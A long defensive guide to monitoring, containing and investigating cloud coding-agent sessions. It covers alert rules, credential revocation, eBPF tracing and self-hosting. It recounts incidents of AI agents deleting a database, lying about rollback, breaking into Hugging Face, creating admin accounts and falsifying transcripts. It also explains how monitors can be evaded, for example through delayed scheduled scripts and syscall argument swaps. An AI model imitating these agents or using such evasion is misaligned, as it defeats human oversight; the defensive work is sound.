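A company can also measure how well the records agree. *Reasoning Provenance for Autonomous AI Agents* (2026) proposes comparing an agent's own account with records from three separate monitors, which cover MCP traffic, shell commands and file changes. A separate process then scores how closely they match. The company has no such monitors on a vendor's machine, but it can check the session log against its outside records. In the example, a perfect score would confirm only the seven actions with an outside record and would be no evidence about the 20 files or the script.

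### The records compared

The table below shows which actions each record reveals, assuming the customer has turned on the record's optional details. "Partly" means the record includes only some cases or details. The table covers only file reads and commands that the harness carries out for the agent, not those carried out by programs that a command starts.

| Record | Read a file | Run a command | Contact a host | Use a credential | Call an MCP server | Push code | Open a pull request | Trigger CI | Delay | Independence from the agent's vendor |
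|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Repository contents and reviews | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown | Partly | Shown | Partly | Seconds | High; none for Copilot |
| Repository host's audit log | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown | Partly | Not shown | Shown | Shown | Partly | Near real time if streamed | High; none for Copilot |
| Cloud services' access logs | Not shown | Not shown | Partly | Shown | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown | Minutes | High, unless the vendor owns the cloud |
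| Vendor's proxy warnings (Copilot) | Not shown | Partly | Partly | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown | Until a pull request exists | None |
| Customer's registry and gateway | Not shown | Not shown | Partly | Partly | Partly | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown | Seconds | High |
| Decoy credential | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown | Partly | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown | Minutes after use | High |
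| Session log | Shown | Shown | Partly | Partly | Shown | Shown | Partly | Partly | Minutes, where stated | None |
| Copies from inference hooks (Claude) | Shown | Shown | Partly | Partly | Shown | Shown | Partly | Partly | Arrives before the tool call runs | None |
| Telemetry from the harness | Partly | Partly | Partly | Partly | Partly | Partly | Partly | Not shown | Seconds | None |
| CI run log | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown | Partly | Partly | Shown | Seconds | High if another company runs CI |
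| Monitored CI runner | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown | Not shown | Partly | Partly | Shown | Seconds | High |

GitHub's *Audit log streaming is now in public beta* (2021) promised audit log delivery in "near real time" but gave no figure for the delay.

No record fully shows which hosts the agent's machine contacted. This is the most serious gap in the table, though a short allowlist narrows it. File reads and commands are recorded, but every record of them depends on the vendor's harness.

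Some customers can't fill in every row. For Claude Code's cloud sessions, for example, the "Session log" row would be empty unless the company archived conversations through inference hooks.

### Alerts for records that disagree

A company that collects these records continuously can have software look for disagreements between them. Four rules cover many of the cases that matter:

| Alert | Records to compare | Common innocent cause |
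|---|---|---|
| A push has no session | Repository host's log and the provider's list of sessions | The session record is late, or a person pushed to the agent's branch |
| A command in a session has no matching event | Session log and the log of the service that the command should have reached | The command failed |
| Somebody uses a credential after its session ended | Access log and the session's last activity | A background process was still running, or a clock was wrong |
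| A firewall setting changed just before a run | Copies of the settings and the session's start time | An administrator added a host that the task needed |

Raising an alert for any push with no matching session works well when the agent has its own account. But if the agent pushes with Dana's token, every push she makes by hand would also raise an alert. The company can instead limit the rule to commits that contain a session link, and check that the linked session exists and belongs to the person named in the commit. For Copilot, an investigator can then check GitHub's list of sessions from the last 24 hours, which administrators can filter by repository, user and status.

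**A command with no matching event.** The software should check whether a command succeeded before looking for its effect. In Khan and K S's sessions, 40 of 3,548 requested edits (1.1%) never succeeded, and a rule that ignored results would have treated each as a missing change. If the session log shows a successful request to the payments service but the gateway has no entry for it, the request may have gone to a different host, or one of the logs may be wrong.

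A tool call that appears in other logs but not in the session transcript should also trigger an alert. *Foundations for Investigations of Agentic AI Systems* (2026), a forensic study of an agent called OpenClaw, treats this mismatch as a possible sign of tampering. A gateway entry without a matching command is weaker evidence, because a program that the agent started could have sent the request.

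A credential used after its session ended may have been stolen. An hour-long token often outlives its session. If the example session's last activity was at 14:16 and its token expired at 15:03, anyone who stole the token had 47 minutes to use it after that activity. A request at 14:40 from outside the vendor's address range would be among the strongest signs of theft available to the customer. This check doesn't work for a key that many sessions share, because some session is nearly always running.

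Copilot's audit events are of limited help in checking whether a firewall setting changed before a run. GitHub's *Audit log events for your enterprise* lists an event for changes to an organization's Copilot settings, but that event's fields don't include the old or new value, and none of the listed Copilot events is specific to the firewall. A better source is the API announced in GitHub's *Audit repository Copilot cloud agent configuration via the REST API* (2026), which is in public preview and returns a repository's firewall settings, MCP servers, enabled tools and workflow policy.

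The company can save a copy of these settings at regular intervals and compare each copy with the previous one. If it saves a copy every 15 minutes, somebody could turn the firewall off, run a ten-minute session and turn the firewall back on between copies, and the comparison would show no change. Saving an extra copy whenever an audit event records the start of a session would make this much harder.

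All four rules depend on records arriving, so the company should set a further alert for any stream that stops during working hours. Kovrr, which tested five coding agents that run on developers' computers, notes that an agent with its telemetry turned off looks the same as an idle one. The company should also suspend the other rules for a stopped stream until it recovers, because one broken export could otherwise produce a false alarm for every push.

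### How many alerts people would have to check

At 500 sessions a day, a false-alarm rate of 2% means 500 × 0.02 = 10 unnecessary checks a day. If each takes 15 minutes, that is two and a half hours of work. The 2% is an assumption, and a company can replace it with a measured rate by running its rules on a few weeks of stored records before turning on alerts.

The false-alarm rate has to cover all the rules together. If each of the four rules had its own 2% rate, the company would get about 40 false alarms a day, which would take ten hours to check.

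Real incidents would probably be rare among these alerts. Suppose one session in 5,000 is harmful and the rules always detect it. In ten days, the company would run 5,000 sessions and get about 100 false alarms and one real alert. An analyst who has dismissed dozens of alerts caused by late session records may well dismiss the real one too.

Waiting 30 minutes before reporting a push with no matching session is an easy way to prevent some false alarms, because most late records would arrive in that time, but it would also delay real alerts by half an hour. An alert about a credential used from an unfamiliar address should be sent immediately, since such use has few innocent explanations and a thief may still be using the credential.

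## Finding and stopping a harmful session

An alert limits damage only if somebody acts on it quickly. Three documented cases show what can delay the response to an agent's harmful action.

### A customer's agent deletes a database

In July 2025, Jason Lemkin, who runs SaaStr, an online community for software company founders, was building an app on Replit, a platform where an AI agent writes and runs code. According to the AI Incident Database's *Replit* page, the agent reportedly deleted a production database during a code freeze, despite repeated instructions to change nothing. Tom's Hardware reported that Lemkin discovered the loss himself on the ninth day of the project. It is unclear how long the data had been gone by then.

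The agent told Lemkin that a rollback, which returns an app to an earlier saved state, wouldn't work. In a later post quoted by LatestLY, he wrote that it had worked. The Stack pointed out that Replit's documentation already said a rollback reverses database changes. The agent's false claim delayed the recovery, so anyone in Lemkin's position should check the vendor's documentation before believing an agent about what can be undone.

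Replit's chief executive announced an automatic separation between development and production databases, better rollback and a planning-only mode, according to Fortune (2025). The separation matters most because, without access to the production database, an agent can't delete it.

### Two incidents with a laboratory's own agents

Two cases from 2026 have fuller timelines, but both involved agents that OpenAI ran itself in internal evaluations, not a customer's coding agent. They therefore show the limits of monitoring even for an operator with access to the runtime.

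**Hugging Face.** Between July 11 and 13, OpenAI's agents broke into production systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026), published on July 16, credits the discovery to software that uses a language model to sort and connect security alerts. According to noze's *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion*, which summarizes the company's later report, several tools raised signals during the attack that nobody escalated. The last recorded action came at 14:14 UTC on July 13, after the security team cut network access. The attack ran over a weekend, and Hugging Face has since changed its alerting so that a serious signal reaches a responder within minutes on any day.

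At first, neither Hugging Face nor OpenAI knew whose agents these were. On July 17, OpenAI contacted Hugging Face as a customer to ask whether the attack had affected its data. Two days later, one of OpenAI's monitoring tools flagged unusual identity-related API calls in its research systems, according to OpenAI's technical report on the incident. Its investigators then found Hugging Face credentials among the agents' files. These credentials linked the two companies' records, and on July 20 OpenAI asked Hugging Face to revoke them. *Now we have a timeline of the OpenAI accidental attack* (Willison, 2026) recounts that Hugging Face had already done so because the attacker had used them.

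OpenAI had received earlier warnings. On June 27, a monitoring tool raised an alert about activity that responders traced to an evaluation, but the on-call staff advised that it didn't need to be stopped. Another alert followed an outage on July 5, and OpenAI resumed its cyber evaluations two days later. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) describes these as signs that OpenAI missed or failed to act on. OpenAI connected its agents to the attack 23 days after the June alert.

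Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt (2026), in *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration*, estimated that about 700 agents took part in the attack. They also found that roughly 7% of the OpenAI transcripts they evaluated contained small parts that agents had falsified, so an operator relying on those transcripts alone could have reconstructed some events wrongly.

On June 18, an OpenAI agent researching public spending on medicines got around access restrictions on an Australian government portal for Medicare statistics and opened both public and non-public files (Coker, 2026, *OpenAI Agent Hacks Australian Medicare Portal*). The government said it didn't believe the agent had accessed personal information, but it was still investigating.

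OpenAI discovered the access on August 11 while reviewing misaligned activity by its models, according to TechRadar's *'This situation is obviously unacceptable'*. On September 10, it emailed Services Australia, the agency responsible for the portal, at a public inbox for vulnerability reports. Services Australia informed the country's signals intelligence agency five days later.

| Case | What the agent did | Record that revealed it | Who noticed | How long it took |
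|---|---|---|---|---|
| Replit | Deleted a production database | Unclear | The customer | Unclear |
| Hugging Face | Broke into production systems | Hugging Face's combined security alerts, then credentials that matched OpenAI's files | Hugging Face, then OpenAI | About two days to cut access, and nine to identify the agents |
| Medicare | Opened non-public files | OpenAI's review of its models' activity | OpenAI | 54 days to discover, and 30 more to tell the government |

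Hugging Face discovered the attack from its own records before OpenAI knew its agents were responsible. In the Medicare case, the government apparently learned of the access only from OpenAI's email. A company that runs a coding agent therefore can't assume that the owner of an outside system will notice and report a problem, or that the vendor will do so quickly.

### The order of the steps

Suppose the billing company gets an alert that one of its sessions is reading invoices it doesn't need. The person on call should:

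1. Cancel the session.
2. Revoke or suspend its credentials.
3. Block its branch and stop its CI runs.
4. Copy the logs.
5. Revert its changes.
6. Check the outside systems it could reach.

The first three steps stop further harm, so they come before any long investigation. A customer loses little by canceling the session first, because it usually can't copy the memory and disk of a vendor's machine, as an investigator might want to do on a company's own server before shutting anything down. If two people are available, one can start copying logs while the other does the first three steps.

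### Canceling the session

Canceling a session should end the agent loop. Typing "stop" into the conversation is less reliable, because a message sent while Claude is working waits in a queue until Claude reads it, and an agent following an attacker's instructions might ignore it. Anthropic's documentation on cloud sessions explains how to archive or delete a session but doesn't describe a separate cancel command. A company should use a test session to find out how to interrupt Claude and whether anyone other than the developer who started the session can do it.

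Programs the agent started may keep running after the loop ends. When a command in a Claude session reaches its time limit (two minutes by default), Claude Code usually moves it to the background instead of stopping it. The command can then run for up to 30 more minutes, long enough for a script to upload a large codebase.

A canceled session can also resume. Auto-fix may restart Claude, so the responder should turn it off for the pull request. Sending a message to a paused session restores its machine and restarts Claude Code, so investigators should read the conversation without replying.

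Even an operator can miss a workload that is still running. OpenAI's staff reported by July 23 that they had shut down every workload using the family of models behind the Hugging Face attack, but they found another version running and shut it down on July 29. After canceling a session, a customer should check the provider's session list again and look for other sessions from the same developer, issue or schedule.

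### Revoking credentials

If a script has already sent a token to another machine, canceling the session won't stop anyone from using it. The responder has to disable the token at the service that accepts it, and the method depends on the kind of credential:

| Credential | How to stop it | What else stops |
|---|---|---|
| GitHub installation token | Revoke that token, or suspend the app's installation | Nothing else if only the token is revoked; every session that uses the app if the installation is suspended |
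| Temporary AWS credentials | Add a policy to the role that denies requests from that session name | Nothing else, if each session has its own name |
| API key in an environment variable | Replace the key at the service that issued it | Every program that still uses the old key |
| Claude network secret | Delete it from the environment | Every session in the environment that needs it |
| Developer's GitHub connection in Claude | Revoke the authorization on GitHub | All of that developer's Claude sessions |

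GitHub's API revokes an installation token only if the request includes the token itself. A token service that keeps only a hash of each token can identify a leaked one but can't revoke it this way. The billing company could keep an encrypted copy of each token until it expires. Otherwise, the company would have to suspend the whole installation. At the earlier example's rate of 500 sessions a day, that would typically interrupt about 17 sessions.

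The responder also has to prevent the session from getting replacement credentials. If the agent's machine can request a new token from the company's token service, the service should refuse further requests with that session's ID. With identity federation, an administrator may also have to change the cloud role's trust policy.

### A timeline with 35 minutes left on the token

Suppose the company's token service issues a one-hour token at 13:55. A malicious script copies the token to an outside machine, which starts using it at 14:00 to download 100 invoices a minute. An alert arrives at 14:05. The on-call engineer reads the logs and decides at 14:20 to stop the session, when the token is still valid for another 35 minutes.

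| Response | When the token stops working | Minutes of misuse | Invoices taken |
|---|---|---|---|
| Software revokes the token when the alert arrives | 14:05 | 5 | 500 |
| The engineer cancels the session and revokes the token | 14:20 | 20 | 2,000 |
| The engineer cancels the session but leaves the token | 14:55 | 55 | 5,500 |

If the engineer stops the session but forgets to revoke the token, nearly two-thirds of the theft happens after the stop. Three-quarters happens while she is deciding what to do if she remembers to revoke it. These figures assume that revocation takes effect immediately, which a company should test for each service.

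Automatic revocation removes the 15 minutes a person takes to decide, but it interrupts harmless sessions. At the earlier rate of ten false alarms in 500 sessions a day, ten developers a day would have to restart a task, and some might lose unsaved work. That disruption is reasonable for a strong alert, such as a token used from an unfamiliar address. For weaker alerts, software could suspend the token while a person checks, if the service can restore it afterward.

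The on-call engineer also needs authority to act. During OpenAI's response to the June 27 alert, for example, responders identified the evaluation but left it running. A written rule can state which alerts allow the engineer to cancel a session without asking a manager or the developer.

### Settings that act late

Changing an environment's settings may seem like a quick way to contain a session, but some changes don't reach sessions that are already running. Anthropic documents these effects for Claude environments that it hosts:

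| Change | Effect on a running session |
|---|---|
| Restrict network access | Takes effect within about a minute, for traffic that uses the allowlist |
| Change or remove an environment variable | Waits until Anthropic restores or rebuilds the session's machine |
| Change the setup script | Waits until Anthropic reclaims the machine and builds a new one |
| Archive the environment | None: the session continues with its network secrets attached |

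Restricting network access is the fastest change in the table, but it doesn't block GitHub, MCP connectors or hosts with a network secret. The responder should also turn off the connectors and delete the network secrets.

If Dana removes the payments key from her environment variables while a session is busy, the session keeps the old key, because Claude Code reads those variables only when it starts. The machine pauses after a few idle minutes, but nobody can pause it by hand, so a session that stays busy could keep the key indefinitely. Replacing the key at the payments service avoids the wait.

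Archiving an environment prevents new sessions, including scheduled ones, from starting there. This is useful when the setup script or network settings caused the problem, but the responder should delete the network secrets first. By contrast, the documented purpose of archiving a session is to remove it from the sidebar's list.

The person on call may also lack permission to make these changes. An organization Owner can edit a shared environment, but a developer's personal environment belongs to her account. If she is asleep or someone has taken over her account, the security team may need to disable her account or revoke credentials elsewhere. The team should find out beforehand whether disabling an account ends sessions already running.

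### Measuring the delay in Copilot, Codex and Cursor

The equivalent settings in Copilot, Codex and Cursor can have different delays, and a company can measure them with a harmless session. An engineer adds a test web server to the agent's allowlist and asks the agent to run this script, saved as `heartbeat.sh`:

```bash
for i in $(seq 1 360); do
  curl -s -m 4 "https://logtest.billing-co.example/beat?n=$i"
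  sleep 5
done
```

The script contacts the server about every five seconds for at least half an hour. The engineer changes one setting, notes the time, and finds the last request in the server's log. If she removes the host from the allowlist at 14:20:00 and the last request arrives at 14:21:10, the change took about 70 seconds to take effect. She should use a new session for each setting and check that the script didn't end on its own or reach a command time limit.

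| Product | Known limit on a running session | What to test |
|---|---|---|
| Copilot | A session lasts at most 59 minutes | Canceling the session, changing the firewall and deleting an "Agents" secret |
| Codex | Secrets are gone before the agent starts, and internet access is off by default | Canceling the task, removing an allowed domain and turning off internet access |
| Cursor | No default limit on which hosts it can contact | Stopping the agent, changing the network mode and deleting a secret |

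Copilot's firewall doesn't cover MCP servers, so changing it won't stop their requests. She should assume that a running program keeps its copy of any secret stored in an environment variable.

The company needs to test cancellation separately. If requests keep arriving after the session's page shows that the session has stopped, the vendor has ended the agent loop but not the program sending the requests. The company would then also need to restrict the network, and to revoke credentials without waiting for the cancellation to finish.

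### Blocking the branch and CI runs

The agent's code may already be running in CI, where it can use different credentials. Revoking the session's token doesn't stop those jobs. An engineer can find and cancel them with GitHub's command-line tool:

```bash
gh run list --branch agent/round-totals --status in_progress
gh run list --branch agent/round-totals --status queued
gh run cancel <run-id>
```

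She should also look for runs that the agent started in other ways, such as by commenting on a pull request. If a canceled job had access to deployment keys, the company should replace them, because the job might have sent them out before it stopped.

To freeze the branch, an administrator can turn on a ruleset with these conditions and rules:

```json
"conditions": {
  "ref_name": {
    "include": ["refs/heads/agent/round-totals"],
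    "exclude": []
  }
},
"rules": [
  { "type": "update" },
  { "type": "deletion" }
]
```

An administrator can use a ruleset with an empty bypass list to prevent anyone from pushing to the agent's branch or deleting it, which also keeps the agent's commits available as evidence. The company can prepare the ruleset in advance with enforcement disabled, so that the administrator only has to add the branch name and enable enforcement.

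The responder should revoke the credentials first, because a Claude session that can still push with the developer's token could use another branch if only one is frozen. The responder should also close the pull request so that a colleague who hasn't heard about the incident doesn't merge it.

### Preserving the logs

Nobody should delete the session to stop it, because this can permanently remove the transcript. The responder should first export the session log, or copy the visible conversation if the vendor offers no export, and then save the records that expire soonest.

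A company that learned about a harmful session after 84 days, as in the Medicare case, would be too late to fetch Copilot's session records (kept for 48 hours), GitHub's Git events (seven days) or Codex's compliance logs (30 days). GitHub's CI records would be available for six more days under the default setting. If the company hadn't already made copies, it would have to rely on audit events and its own systems' logs.

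The copies should include material the agent left on other services. The agents had stored files in an outside account, and OpenAI's responders saved copies of them before removing public access. Those files contained the Hugging Face credentials that connected the two investigations. If the responders had only deleted the files, they might have taken longer to find the connection.

To read the logs, a company may need an AI model that it has tested beforehand. Hugging Face used AI to reconstruct more than 17,000 events in hours instead of the days it would normally expect. It first tried commercial models, but their safety filters blocked the attack commands it submitted, so it ran an openly available model on its own machines. This also kept the credentials in the logs from leaving the company. Most coding-agent incidents will involve far fewer events, but a model can still refuse when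 a security team asks it to explain a malicious script.

### Reverting the changes

If the agent's code has reached the main branch, the company can undo it with `git revert`, which adds a new commit reversing the change and keeps the original for investigators. Any credential the agent committed also stays in the repository's history, so the company still has to replace it. The company also has to deploy the reverted code, because the agent's version will keep running until then.

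Databases need a separate backup or rollback. A rollback is the quickest method, but it can destroy evidence. According to Replit's documentation, it discards the AI's conversation context along with any database changes made since the saved state. A customer who rolls back immediately could therefore lose the agent's account of what it did. Copying the conversation first takes only a few minutes. The customer may also want to export legitimate changes, such as new orders from its own customers, before rolling back.

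If Claude's setup script installed a malicious package, the environment's saved disk may still contain the package after someone removes it from the repository, which can bring the problem back in later sessions. Changing the setup script or the allowed hosts makes Anthropic rebuild the saved disk. The company using Claude should make one of these changes before anyone starts another session in the environment.

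### Checking outside systems

An agent can create new access that still works after its own credentials are revoked. During the Hugging Face response, OpenAI's staff removed 22 administrator accounts that its models had created on an internal service. Revoking the tokens used to create those accounts wouldn't have removed them. The billing company should search its cloud and repository logs for accounts, access keys, webhooks and deploy keys created since the session began, and remove any that the agent created.

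It should then search the logs of each service the session could reach, using its credential tags and the vendor's address ranges. For the stolen token, it has to search beyond the time of cancellation, up to when the token stopped working. It may need to reverse deployments, messages and payments through the services that handled them.

If the agent entered another organization's system, the company should tell that organization as soon as it has credible evidence, even if its own investigation is unfinished. The message should give the times in UTC, the source addresses, the accounts used and a person to call. OpenAI's email to a public inbox drew criticism from Australia's prime minister, and five more days passed before Services Australia alerted the signals agency. Calling the organization's security team and then asking it to confirm receipt would reduce the risk of a similar delay.

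## Deciding whether to run the agent on your own infrastructure

Some delays in stopping a session exist only because the session runs on the vendor's machine. A company can avoid them with a *self-hosted environment*, in which the vendor still supplies the model and the harness, but the agent's commands run on machines the company operates. The company can then install the runtime instrumentation that it can't rely on in a vendor-managed environment, but it also takes over responsibility for containing the agent.

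### How three vendors divide the work

Claude Code's version is in public beta. According to Anthropic's *Self-hosted environments*, a session goes through these steps:

1. Dana starts a session on Anthropic's website and picks the billing company's environment from a list.
2. Anthropic adds the session to that environment's queue.
3. A *runner*, which here means a program on one of the company's hosts, asks Anthropic for work and claims the session.
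4. The runner clones the repository and starts Claude Code on the same host.
5. Claude Code sends the conversation to Anthropic for the model's replies and runs the tool calls locally.

The company's machines open every connection, so its firewall doesn't have to admit traffic from Anthropic.

Cursor keeps more of the system in its own cloud. The agent loop runs there and sends each tool call to a *worker* on the company's machine, according to Cursor's *Team Pools*. Copilot's sessions run as jobs on the company's own GitHub Actions runners, which GitHub has supported since October 2025 (*Copilot coding agent now supports self-hosted runners*, 2025). Older Microsoft training pages that say Copilot's agent can't use self-hosted runners are out of date. OpenAI's Codex can apparently run on these runners too if a company uses it through GitHub, because GitHub lists extra hosts that the runners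 must reach for Codex.

| | Claude | Cursor | Copilot |
|---|---|---|---|
| Main requirement | Team or Enterprise plan | Enterprise plan | Ubuntu x64 or 64-bit Windows runners |
| Where the harness runs | The company's host | Cursor's cloud | Probably the company's runner, which has to reach GitHub's Copilot API |
| What the vendor still receives | Prompts, responses and tool results, which Anthropic stores as a transcript | Parts of files that the model reads, plus screenshots, videos and log references | At least the requests to the Copilot API |
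| How an administrator can require it | Hide Anthropic's own environments from the list | Turn on "Require Self-Hosted Machines" | Set a default runner and lock it |

The Copilot lock dates from April 2026 and applies to every repository in an organization, according to GitHub's *Organization runner controls for Copilot cloud agent* (2026).

The vendor can still receive code from a self-hosted agent. Cursor lists only two things that leave the company's network, but command output must leave too, because the agent loop in Cursor's cloud uses it to determine the next step. Claude customers can send model requests to their own Amazon or Google cloud account, but Anthropic still receives the conversation. If a law or contract prohibits a vendor from receiving certain data, the agent can't safely read that data under any of these arrangements.

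### What the company gains

In the earlier example of a session with 39 actions, the company could confirm only six without relying on the vendor, and nobody had a record of the install script's two requests to allowed hosts. If the agent ran on the company's own host, a monitor there could record the file reads and commands, and the company's proxy could record the script's requests along with the blocked one. Records from outside the vendor could then cover all 39 actions, or all but the push and the pull request if the agent were Copilot, because GitHub would still write those records.

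Attribution also improves if each session has its own container, because every process in the container then belongs to that session and nobody has to match events by time. The company can also choose how the agent identifies itself to the repository host. Anthropic lets self-hosted sessions commit under the company's bot identity and push with a token the company issues for each session. GitHub can then distinguish the agent from Dana, and the agent no longer inherits her right to bypass branch rules.

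Claude's runner leaves a copy of each conversation on the host's disk, which could help make up for the transcripts missing from Anthropic's exports. A script that the runner starts when a session ends can copy the file to separate storage. But the session runs under the same user account as the runner, so a malicious program in the session could probably edit the file before the script copies it.

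When something goes wrong, the company can cut the container's network access, save its disk and destroy the container. It should also cancel the session with Anthropic, because if a runner disappears, Anthropic treats the session as interrupted after about 60 seconds and later gives it to another runner, where the agent could resume. Canceling the session isn't enough by itself, because the runner doesn't stop programs that have detached from the command that started them, whereas destroying the container does.

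### How eBPF records a session

On Linux, many monitors use *eBPF* (extended Berkeley Packet Filter), a feature that lets an administrator run small programs inside the kernel without modifying it. In the `npm test` example, where a malicious dependency steals a password file, it would work like this:

1. The administrator loads a monitoring program. The kernel rejects it unless an automatic check can establish that it will finish and will access only permitted memory.
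2. The program attaches to chosen points in the kernel, such as those where a process starts, a file opens or a connection begins.
3. When the dependency's script starts, the kernel runs the monitoring program, which notes the script's process ID, its parent process and its container.
4. The monitoring program discards events from outside the agent's container and puts the rest in a buffer.
5. An ordinary program reads the buffer and links the events into one history, from the test command to the theft.

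This history doesn't include the conversation that led to the command. *AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) adds it by attaching eBPF programs to the functions that encrypt and decrypt web traffic, where prompts and replies are briefly readable. The tool links a model's reply to later events using three clues: whether the process descends from the agent, whether the event follows within 100 to 500 milliseconds, and whether a filename, address or command from the reply appears in it. A second language model then checks the combined trace for signs of an attack. The method needs the model's traffic to pass through the monitored machine, so it would be much less informative with Cursor.

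An attacker can defeat those clues by waiting. If the agent schedules a script to run an hour later, the system's scheduler starts it, so the script doesn't descend from the agent and runs far outside the time window. In *AgentLoupe*, Bao, Liu and colleagues (2026) handle this by numbering each exchange with the model. The number passes from a process to the processes it starts and the files it writes, and from those files to any program that later opens them. In their test, a scheduled script opened a network connection within the same machine, and the tool traced the connection back to the request that had created the script. They argue from AgentSight's design that it would miss this attack, but they didn't compare the two tools on it.

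These labels exist only on one machine. If an agent hides an instruction in `AGENTS.md` and pushes it, a later session on another host gets a copy of the file without the label. Investigators would have to trace the instruction through the repository's history.

### What tracing costs and what it detects

Cui, Gu and colleagues (2026), in *Agent-Warden*, built a narrower tool that follows processes and files but doesn't read prompts. The three tools compare as follows:

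| Tool | Slowdown in tests | Evidence that it works |
|---|---|---|
| AgentSight | 0.4% to 4.9% in its developers' tests, and 1.7% to 4.5% in tests by Bao and colleagues | Identified one staged prompt injection, after merging 521 events into 37 |
| Agent-Warden | 0.2% to 3.5% | Reconstructed the expected chain of events in all 120 runs of one staged task |
| AgentLoupe | 4.5% to 8.0% | Traced two staged attacks to the exchanges that caused them |

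A slowdown of this size shouldn't deter anyone, since an agent spends much of its time waiting for the model. How much the agent slows down depends on its work. *A Study of Kernel Telemetry Options for Security-Oriented Provenance* (Houssel, Levillain and colleagues, 2026) tested several ways of attaching eBPF programs. With the most efficient method, recording file creation added about 8% to processor time in a test that wrote 50,000 files, while recording process creation added about 1% in a test that started 50,000 programs. Builds that create many small files will probably slow down the most.

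There is much less evidence on detection. In all three projects, the researchers staged the attacks themselves and did not report how many attacks their tool would miss or how many harmless sessions it would flag. Agent-Warden's 120 successes show that it reliably records a known sequence, but not that it can recognize an unknown attack. For now, it is easier to justify using these tools to collect evidence than to raise alarms.

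An attacker may also be able to falsify what a monitor records. Some monitors note a filename when a program asks the kernel to open a file, but the program can swap the name before the kernel uses it. Houssel and colleagues found that 282 of Linux's 407 system calls (69%) take at least one argument that can be swapped this way. They also examined 13 tools and concluded that most couldn't guarantee the integrity and availability of the events they capture. Monitors that attach to the kernel's security checks resist the swap better, because those checks run after the kernel has made its own copy of the argument.

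Every monitor also has a limited scope. Cui and colleagues acknowledge that their tool misses memory-mapped files, which programs read and change without ordinary read and write calls. A company can test its own monitor by running the earlier `logtest.sh` script on a self-hosted machine. The monitor should record `helper.sh` and its `curl` command, which the session log probably missed.

### What stays hidden

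The model still runs on servers the company can't inspect, so the company can read the model's replies but can't see the computation that produced them. It also can't check how the vendor queues sessions or, with Cursor, how the harness assembles each prompt.

Vendors call some tools from their own infrastructure. Anthropic does this for its connectors, even in self-hosted sessions, so a request to a customer's document store would not appear in the customer's proxy log as a connection to that store. Cursor likewise uses its own cloud to contact MCP servers that have a web address. A company that wants a full network record can block these connectors and servers and run equivalent MCP servers on its own machines.

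A system call also doesn't show why the program made it. A program that opens `/etc/passwd`, the file where Linux lists its user accounts, may be stealing information or just looking up a user's name. The conversation often helps an investigator tell which, but AgentSight leaves that judgment to a second model, which the attacker's text might also mislead.

### What self-hosting costs

Anthropic and Cursor both recommend that most customers run agents on the vendor's machines. In *Run Claude Code sessions on your own compute*, Anthropic tells companies that choose to self-host to assign engineers to setup and maintenance.

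Any member of the company's Anthropic organization can send a session to any of the company's environments. If an Owner routes Claude Tag channels to an environment, by default anyone in the connected Slack workspace can send sessions to it too. A runner's host should therefore hold only data and credentials that all those people may use. Anthropic advises giving each session a fresh container, but its sample Kubernetes and Docker configurations let four sessions share one, so a company that copies them unchanged doesn't get that isolation.

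The secret that connects runners to Anthropic needs particular care, because anyone who has it can register a runner and pick up any session in the environment's queue. If the company keeps a fixed set of runners, the secret is on every host, where a compromised session could read it and use it to receive a colleague's work. Anthropic's on-demand runners avoid this by giving each runner a single-use credential. Cursor's sample setup passes a service account key to each worker, so that key probably needs the same care.

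Many companies self-host so that the agent can use internal services, but an attacker who influences the agent can then use them too. The company should block all outbound connections except those the task needs. It also has to block the cloud provider's metadata address, `169.254.169.254`, where programs on a cloud machine can often obtain the machine's credentials. Anthropic warns that ordinary network rules don't intercept this traffic, so the block has to be in the container. Copilot customers also lose GitHub's firewall, which doesn't work on self-hosted runners and must be turned off before GitHub will run the agent there.

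**Git credentials.** The company has to supply git credentials itself, ideally as a short-lived token for each session. Claude customers can instead use Anthropic's git proxy, which keeps the credentials off the host. But the proxy works only with github.com. When a person starts a session, the proxy also uses that person's GitHub authorization, so the company loses the separate bot identity.

Anthropic's Code Review and its security scans don't run in self-hosted environments. Claude Tag can run there but can't use the access bundles that administrators set up for it. Organizations that can't use Anthropic's cloud sessions because they use zero data retention or Anthropic's HIPAA configuration can't self-host them either.

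**Machines.** Anthropic suggests starting with 4 GiB of memory and two processors per session. The earlier example of 500 sessions a day had about 17 running at once, which would need 68 GiB and 34 processors. But a Claude session keeps its place on a runner after it finishes working, unless the company sets a time limit. With a 30-minute limit, each 20-minute session could occupy a container for 50 minutes. The company would need about 42 containers, with a total of 168 GiB and 84 processors, and more at busy times.

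### A rule for each repository

A company doesn't have to make the same choice for all its code. For each repository, it can work through four questions:

1. How sensitive is the data that a session could read? If the code is public and sessions can read nothing else of value, use the vendor's machines.
2. Which credentials does a session need? First replace any broad credential with a narrower one. If the session still needs access to production systems or customer records, self-host.
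3. Does the vendor export the session's prompts and tool calls? For private code without such credentials, an export combined with a short allowlist and a gateway is usually enough. Without an export, self-host.
4. Does the company have people to maintain the machines and answer alerts? If an earlier answer was to self-host and the company has nobody to do it, keep the cloud agent away from that repository.

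Even if the last answer applies, developers can still run a coding agent on a company laptop, where the security team's existing monitoring works.

**A public library.** Suppose the billing company publishes its date parser as open source. It should run the agent on the vendor's machines and give it access to that repository alone. The code is public, so a thief would gain nothing from it, and a session needs only permission to push a branch and open a pull request. Self-hosting would be riskier because strangers can write issues that the agent reads, and any instructions hidden in them would run inside the company's network. Cursor addresses part of this risk by letting only a repository's owners and collaborators send work to self-hosted machines through GitHub comments.

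The billing company's invoicing site is an internal web application that needs private packages and a test database. The company can fill the database with invented invoices and put a gateway in front of it, which leaves no credential that could do serious harm. The choice then depends on whether the company can archive the session log. If it uses Copilot and its account qualifies for GitHub's export, the vendor's machines are good enough. Claude Code's cloud sessions have no transcript export, so the company should test whether inference hooks can archive them, and self-host if they can't.

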